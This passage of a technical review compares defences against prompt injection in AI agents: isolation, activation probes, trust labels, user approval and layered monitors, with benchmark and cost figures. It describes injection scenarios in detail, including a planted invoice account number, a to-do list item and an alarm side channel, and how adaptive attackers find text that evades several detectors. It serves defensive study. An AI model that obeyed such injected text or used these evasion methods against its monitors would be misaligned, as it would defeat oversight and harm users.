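Foerster and colleagues report that isolation keeps up to 57% of a frontier model's performance on computer-use tasks, but this figure allows five attempts per task. They tested an isolated version of Claude Sonnet 4.5 on 109 tasks that the model had solved without isolation. It solved 62 at least once (57%), but only 31 on the first attempt (28%). The higher figure assumes that something can pick out the successful attempt. With three attempts, a small open model appeared to do better with isolation, but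 on the first attempt the isolated version solved 51 of 339 tasks, compared with 60 for the undefended agent.

### Tokens

The CaMeL paper puts its token use on AgentDojo at roughly 2.8 times that of an undefended agent. Foerster and colleagues measured the overhead on 17 computer-use tasks:

| Set-up | Tokens relative to no defence | Cost of the test |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | 1.88 times | $5.40 |
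| CaMeL with both extra checks against branch steering | 6.57 times | $18.37 |
| FIDES | 29.6 times | $76.07 |

CaMeL's ratio is probably lower here than on AgentDojo because reading screenshots already takes many tokens. But the ratio understates the cost, because CaMeL generated about 35 times as many output tokens as the undefended agent, mostly in its long plans, and providers charge more for output than for input.

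FIDES was so expensive because it sent the planner the full history again at every step. The expense comes from planning a long task one step at a time, and the labels themselves add little to it. On short browser tasks, an agent built on FIDES needed about as many turns as an undefended one.

### Approval by the user

When a policy blocks an action, the system can ask the user for approval instead of abandoning the task. This recovers many lost tasks, but it takes the user's time and makes security depend on the user's attention. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) argue in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that earlier comparisons were unfair to defended agents because they counted a task as failed if it needed approval, while the undefended agent could act freely. Many products already ask the user before every consequential action.

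Kolluri and colleagues therefore count approvals. For *n* tasks, let *vᵢ* be the number of actions in task *i* that break the policy and need approval. The completion rate with at most *k* approvals per task is

TCR@*k* = (number of tasks completed with *vᵢ* ≤ *k*) / *n*.

TCR@0 is the share of tasks that the agent completes entirely on its own. On AgentDojo with o3-mini, the results were:

| Agent | Approvals over all completed tasks | TCR@0 |
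|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential action | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Ordinary loop with labels | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

Prudentia, Kolluri and colleagues' own system, adds information about labels and policies to FIDES's planner so the planner can avoid steps that would need approval. Isolation gives users more freedom than an agent that always asks for approval, but it still appears to have significant drawbacks compared with one that never asks.

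Isolation has almost no drawbacks when the task doesn't depend on text written by strangers. Kolluri and colleagues also tested Prudentia on WASP, a benchmark in which a browser agent comments on a post or upvotes it while the page contains an injection. Prudentia hid all user-written text from the planner. No attack succeeded and no action needed approval. With every model, the agent completed at least as many tasks as it did undefended, because the injections no longer distracted it. WASP has only these two user tasks, though, and neither requires the agent to understand the post.

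Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a whole document instead of approving each action. For an email with ten things to do, the user answers one question instead of ten. This is convenient but riskier, because the user is no longer shown each specific action, such as a payment to a stranger. If they endorse the email without noticing a planted sentence, the planner will treat that sentence as trusted too.

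Kolluri and colleagues find that no attack succeeds, but this result depends partly on their assumption that people reject every malicious action. They cite research on *confirmation fatigue*, in which people who see too many security prompts start approving them without thinking. Fixed rules trigger Prudentia's requests for approval, so an attacker can't prevent them but may influence the text that the user sees.

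### What an agent guarded only by a probe can still do

An agent defended only by a probe keeps its ordinary loop, so it can read a to-do list and carry it out, change its plan when a login page appears, or take an account number from a file. Nobody has to write policies or label data. In Dong and colleagues' tests, Qwen3-8B completed slightly more clean tasks with the probe and its inserted warning than with no defence. The probe also adds negligible computation compared with CaMeL's extra planning.

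This freedom depends on how the system responds to an alarm. On AgentDyn, where every task has a helpful instruction to follow, two text filters blocked so much that GPT-4o's task completion fell from 53% to 0% with one and 10% with the other. A probe that blocks tool results could cause similar losses. Even Kale and Vishwanath's improved probe flagged 15% of harmless instructions in new applications. Dong and colleagues' probe ranked attacks well on a mixture of data that included AgentDyn, but that result doesn't measure how many tasks its alarms would interrupt. Sending alarms to a second check would let the agent complete more tasks.

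An agent with a probe is free to follow instructions it finds in data, so it can also follow any injection the probe misses. If a stranger adds "renew the domain with this provider" to a shared to-do list, the item may look like all the others, and the agent will probably complete it along with the rest. CaMeL can't carry out the list at all unless its plan lets the list determine which actions to take.

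## Can a probe be combined with isolation without losing the guarantee?

A probe can be added to an isolated agent without weakening the guarantee if the probe can only remove permissions. It can block a call, mark data as less trusted or require the user's approval, all of which leave the agent at least as restricted as before. If a low probe score can mark data as safe, the guarantee is limited by the probe's detection rate.

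### Adding and removing restrictions

Let *P* be the set of tool calls that the policy permits, and let *D*(*x*) be the calls that remain after the probe has scored the untrusted data *x*. If a call must pass both checks, the agent can make only the calls in

*P* ∩ *D*(*x*) ⊆ *P*.

This holds for every *x*, so even a probe that misses every attack can't weaken the guarantee. If a low score instead unlocks some extra calls *E*, such as sending mail to new recipients, the agent can make any call in *P* ∪ *E* whenever the probe misses an attack, and an attacker needs only one text that the probe misses. *Agentic AI Defense* (2026) says that a detector "fails open on anything it did not anticipate". *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) concludes that detection can't replace confinement, but the two can be combined.

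A limited form of removal is also possible. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) describes a system in which reading new data can only reduce an agent's permissions. Results from an unlabelled tool count as "unknown", and a classifier may label them later, but only up to a level of trust that the developer fixed in advance. A model may also, within a fixed mandate, approve single calls that the policy would otherwise block. If the mandate covers mail to colleagues, an attacker who fools the model can get any mail to colleagues approved, but no mail to a stranger. Kravchenko and colleagues therefore claim only that every exception is authorised and logged, which is weaker than noninterference.

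### The invoice with each kind of probe

Suppose CaMeL handles the request to find and pay the invoice, and a probe reads the quarantined model's activations while that model processes the email. If the probe raises an alarm, the run stops. Attack A, the email asking for all mail to be sent to a stranger, already fails without the probe. The probe is more useful against an email that tells the quarantined model to return the thief's account number. A lenient payment policy would let that number through, but the probe may well flag the instruction. In attack B, the probe will probably raise no alarm, and the payment policy then allows or blocks the payment exactly as it would without a probe.

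Suppose FIDES normally hides the email from its planner, but a developer adds a rule that an email with a low probe score counts as trusted. If attack A gets past the probe, the planner reads the email in a trusted context and may forward the mail. A policy that checks only the context's label will allow this.

Attack B is even more effective under this rule because it contains no instruction, so its score is low and the false account number becomes trusted. Even a strict policy that requires a trusted recipient would then allow the payment to the thief. A low score is no reason to change the label, because the probe estimates whether a text contains an injection, while the label records whether an outsider could have chosen the text.

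### Side effects of extra restrictions

Blocking the agent when a probe raises an alarm can leak information, because the probe's score may reflect everything in the prompt, including the user's private files. An attacker could try to write an email that triggers the alarm only if those files contain a certain word, then watch whether the agent replies. That would reveal one bit per email, much like the leak from CaMeL's blocked programs. Scoring the email in a separate run, without the private files, removes this leak because the score then depends only on the attacker's text.

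The guarantee also depends on how the agent responds to an alarm. Under the noninterference theorem for LLMbda, untrusted data can stop a run but cannot replace one trusted result with another, so stopping when there is an alarm is safe. If the agent instead pays last month's account, an outsider can choose between two payments by triggering or avoiding the alarm.

False alarms cost utility, and an attacker can cause them on purpose by filling an inbox with suspicious text. They can also weaken security if the guarantee relies on a person who approves exceptions. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) simulates a reviewer who catches a bad call with probability

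0.9 × max(0.3, 1 − 0.3*L*) × 0.93^*k*,

where *L* is the average number of harmless requests for approval per task, and *k* counts earlier attack attempts and approval requests. At the start of a campaign, the reviewer misses 10% of bad calls if there are no harmless requests, 37% if there is one per task and 64% if there are two. These numbers are assumptions, not measurements of real people, but the direction is plausible. A probe that often asks for approval could make the user less careful about the requests that matter, so it may be better to send its alarms to a second model first.

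### Dropping a label together with the data

Letting a model remove labels is tempting because labels spread quickly. Giving a model's output the labels of all its inputs is sound, as Costa and colleagues note, but may be too conservative, since most of those inputs may not have affected the output.

Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, found a safe way to drop labels. Their system works in three steps:

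1. The model answers using all the documents.
2. The system removes the untrusted documents and calculates how likely the same answer would be without them.
3. If the answer is still nearly as likely, the model writes a new answer from the trusted documents alone, and the system returns this one with a trusted label.

A mistake in the model's judgement makes the answer worse but doesn't make the label wrong, because the untrusted documents were absent when the model wrote the final answer.

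Suppose the prompt contains both the emailed invoice and a trusted list of suppliers' accounts. If the invoice is genuine, its account number matches the list, so the answer stays likely without the email and the new answer gets a trusted label. If the model has copied a thief's account number from the invoice, that answer becomes very unlikely without the email, so the label stays untrusted and a strict policy blocks the payment. Without the list, the system can't drop the untrusted label even for a genuine invoice, because the account number appears only in the email.

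Siddiqui and colleagues tested this on 40 short agent conversations, 20 of which allowed a better label. The system improved the label in 17 of the 20 with a small Llama 2 model and in 19 with a large one. On questions about news articles, the small model improved 57% of the 647 labels that could be improved, but 23% of the improvements left out a document that the answer needed. The system's guarantee covers what the answer says, but the removed documents still affect whether the answer gets the better label. Someone who sees only public answers could therefore learn a little from whether an answer appears. An attacker can also prevent the label from improving by adding distracting text.

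*RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) applies the same principle before each tool call. A *screener* picks out the parts of the conversation that the next step needs. The system combines their labels and hides everything with a label more restrictive than the combined one, then the agent chooses its call. If the combined label breaks the tool's policy, the user has to confirm the call. The screener is either a language model or a small network that analyses a second model's attention weights. The network was right only 81% of the time on test data, but a wrong choice can only hide something useful or cause an unnecessary confirmation.

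On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated its policy. This excludes one workspace case because the possible injection was in text labelled as the user's own. With the language-model screener, utility fell by less than 1% under attack and by 10% without attacks. With the attention screener, it fell by 3% and 7.4%. On Slack tasks, which often require acting on web pages, the agent completed only 22% and 33% respectively. The tests skipped every call that needed confirmation, so a real user could have rescued some tasks by approving those calls. The attention screener was also trained on 40 AgentDojo cases, which may have inflated its results. Both versions used about twice as many tokens as an undefended agent.

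### Dropping a label but keeping the data

Other systems drop a label while the data stays in the prompt. In *Sightline*, Xu, Li and colleagues (2026) trained a classifier on attention weights to predict which inputs a model's output used. They set its threshold to miss at most 1% of real dependencies on average. At that setting, it removed 44% to 66% of unnecessary labels, depending on the model, and no attack got past an integrity policy in their agent test.

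The 1% limit depends on new calls resembling the ones used to set the threshold, and attackers have a strong incentive to write text that differs. Xu and colleagues also prove that an output can depend on an input even when attention to that input is weak. Their method is a well-calibrated detector, but a policy that relies on its labels is no longer guaranteed to hold for every input.

*GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) instead estimates how much the output would change if a passage changed slightly. Its proof covers only small changes around one prompt, but an attacker can write any text. Xu and colleagues note that such measures also shrink in proportion to 1 − *p*, where *p* is the probability the model gave to the token it wrote. If a model copies each digit of an account number from an invoice with probability 0.999, this factor is 0.001, and the invoice could appear to have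 almost no influence on the number.

### When a model must notice the danger first

*SafeFlow* (Dai, Ying and colleagues, 2026), a system for groups of cooperating agents, follows the rule that a model may only add restrictions. A language model labels parts of the work, for example as access to credentials, but can't clear a label. Fixed rules carry the labels from agent to agent and hold back irreversible actions until the whole workflow has passed a check.

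Even so, attacks still succeeded 12.7% of the time on average, compared with 69.3% without a defence. The rate was 22.7% when the attacks were adapted to hide the evidence. Many of these attacks were harmful requests from users, so the rates aren't comparable with AgentDojo's. Attacks can succeed when the model fails to label a dangerous source or the record lacks a link between two agents' steps, because the fixed rules then have nothing to act on. Adding restrictions preserves an existing guarantee but can't create one where safety depends on a model noticing the danger. Dai and colleagues accordingly claim only that the rules are deterministic once the labels are fixed, not that the whole system is.

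### Tracking leaked credentials

*Caught in the Act(ivation)* (Chauhan and Revankar, 2026) combines a probe with two other monitors. The probe analyses activations at the end of the prompt, before the agent writes anything. The second monitor plants fake credentials and checks whether they appear in the output. The third estimates how much each reply reveals about a password or key and blocks the conversation when the total reaches a limit.

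On single prompts, the probe had an AUROC of 0.998 with a 1.5% false-positive rate. A separate test of the running total used 50 invented conversations, each with 20 turns and four to eight attempts to leak a little information. The running total caught 90% of the conversations, compared with 12% for a text filter that checked each turn on its own. The conversations it missed ended before the total reached the limit.

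This looks like information-flow control but gives no comparable guarantee. A guarantee would need an upper bound on the information leaked, but the estimator approximates a *lower* bound, so the true leak may be larger. An attacker could also reset the total by starting a new conversation. The prototype doesn't check credentials passed in tool calls, although agents often use credentials this way. Chauhan and Revankar acknowledge these limits and suggest adding explicit labels.

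### Do layers fail independently?

If one layer misses 5% of attacks and another misses 10%, independence would mean that both miss 0.5%. If every attack that the better layer misses also gets past the other, both miss 5%, ten times as many. In general, with miss rates *m*₁ and *m*₂ and a correlation ρ between the misses, the combined miss rate is

*m*₁*m*₂ + ρ√(*m*₁(1 − *m*₁)*m*₂(1 − *m*₂)).

A correlation of only 0.3 gives about 2.5%. Chauhan and Revankar report enough figures for a rough comparison:

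| Layers | Missed by each alone | Missed by both if independent | Missed in the test |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fake credentials with running total; probe | 29%, 12% | 3.5% | 6% |
| Fake credentials; input filter | 70%, 40% | 28% | 18% |

The first pair missed more attacks than independence predicts, and the second missed fewer, presumably because the fake credentials and the input filter catch different attacks. The thresholds were retuned for the full system, so the first comparison is only suggestive. Even so, the miss rate of a combination clearly needs to be measured, not just calculated by multiplying the individual miss rates.

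These figures also assume fixed attacks. An adaptive attacker can take the texts that get past the first layer and search among them for one that also gets past the second. If both layers respond to commanding language, a calmer wording may evade both. If the attacker then reuses that text against the same setup, its combined miss rate may be close to 100%, whatever the average was. Even at a miss rate of 0.5% per attempt, an attacker trying texts at random would need only about 200 tries to find one.

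Layers are more likely to complement each other if they check different things. A probe responds to a text's content, while a policy checks which action the agent takes and where the action's values came from. This makes them a better pair than two classifiers trained on similar attacks, which is a reason to take Anthropic's results for auto mode seriously. But attack B still gets past both if the policy allows payments to untrusted accounts.

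### Matching the defence to the agent

Isolation works best for fixed workflows, such as paying invoices from known suppliers, because the steps are known in advance. *SPA* (2026) describes a system that checks a whole plan before running it and gives each action the labels of the conditions it depends on. A probe on the quarantined model adds little overhead and can alert the company to an attack.

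An agent that browses the web has to adapt to what it finds, so planning every step in advance rarely works. A probe can screen the pages it reads, while least privilege limits its payments and messages. Some isolation is still possible in APPA, where an agent can read a page in a temporary copy of its conversation and bring back only a few fields in a fixed format, such as a ticket number and a severity level. With one model, removing this option reduced the share of company tasks completed from 88% to 56.5%. A malicious page can still supply a false severity level, so someone has to justify endorsing that field as trusted.

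Coding agents often have to act on bug reports and documentation written by strangers. The most important layers of protection are a sandbox with restricted network access and a code review before deployment. A probe can flag suspicious documentation, but the network restrictions should stay in place even when the probe's score is low.

A company that uses a model through an API can still apply labels, sandboxes and permission rules, because these work outside the model. For screening, it can run a smaller open model alongside the API model, as RTBAS did with GPT-4o. The two models don't have to match exactly, as long as screening can only add restrictions or remove data along with its label.
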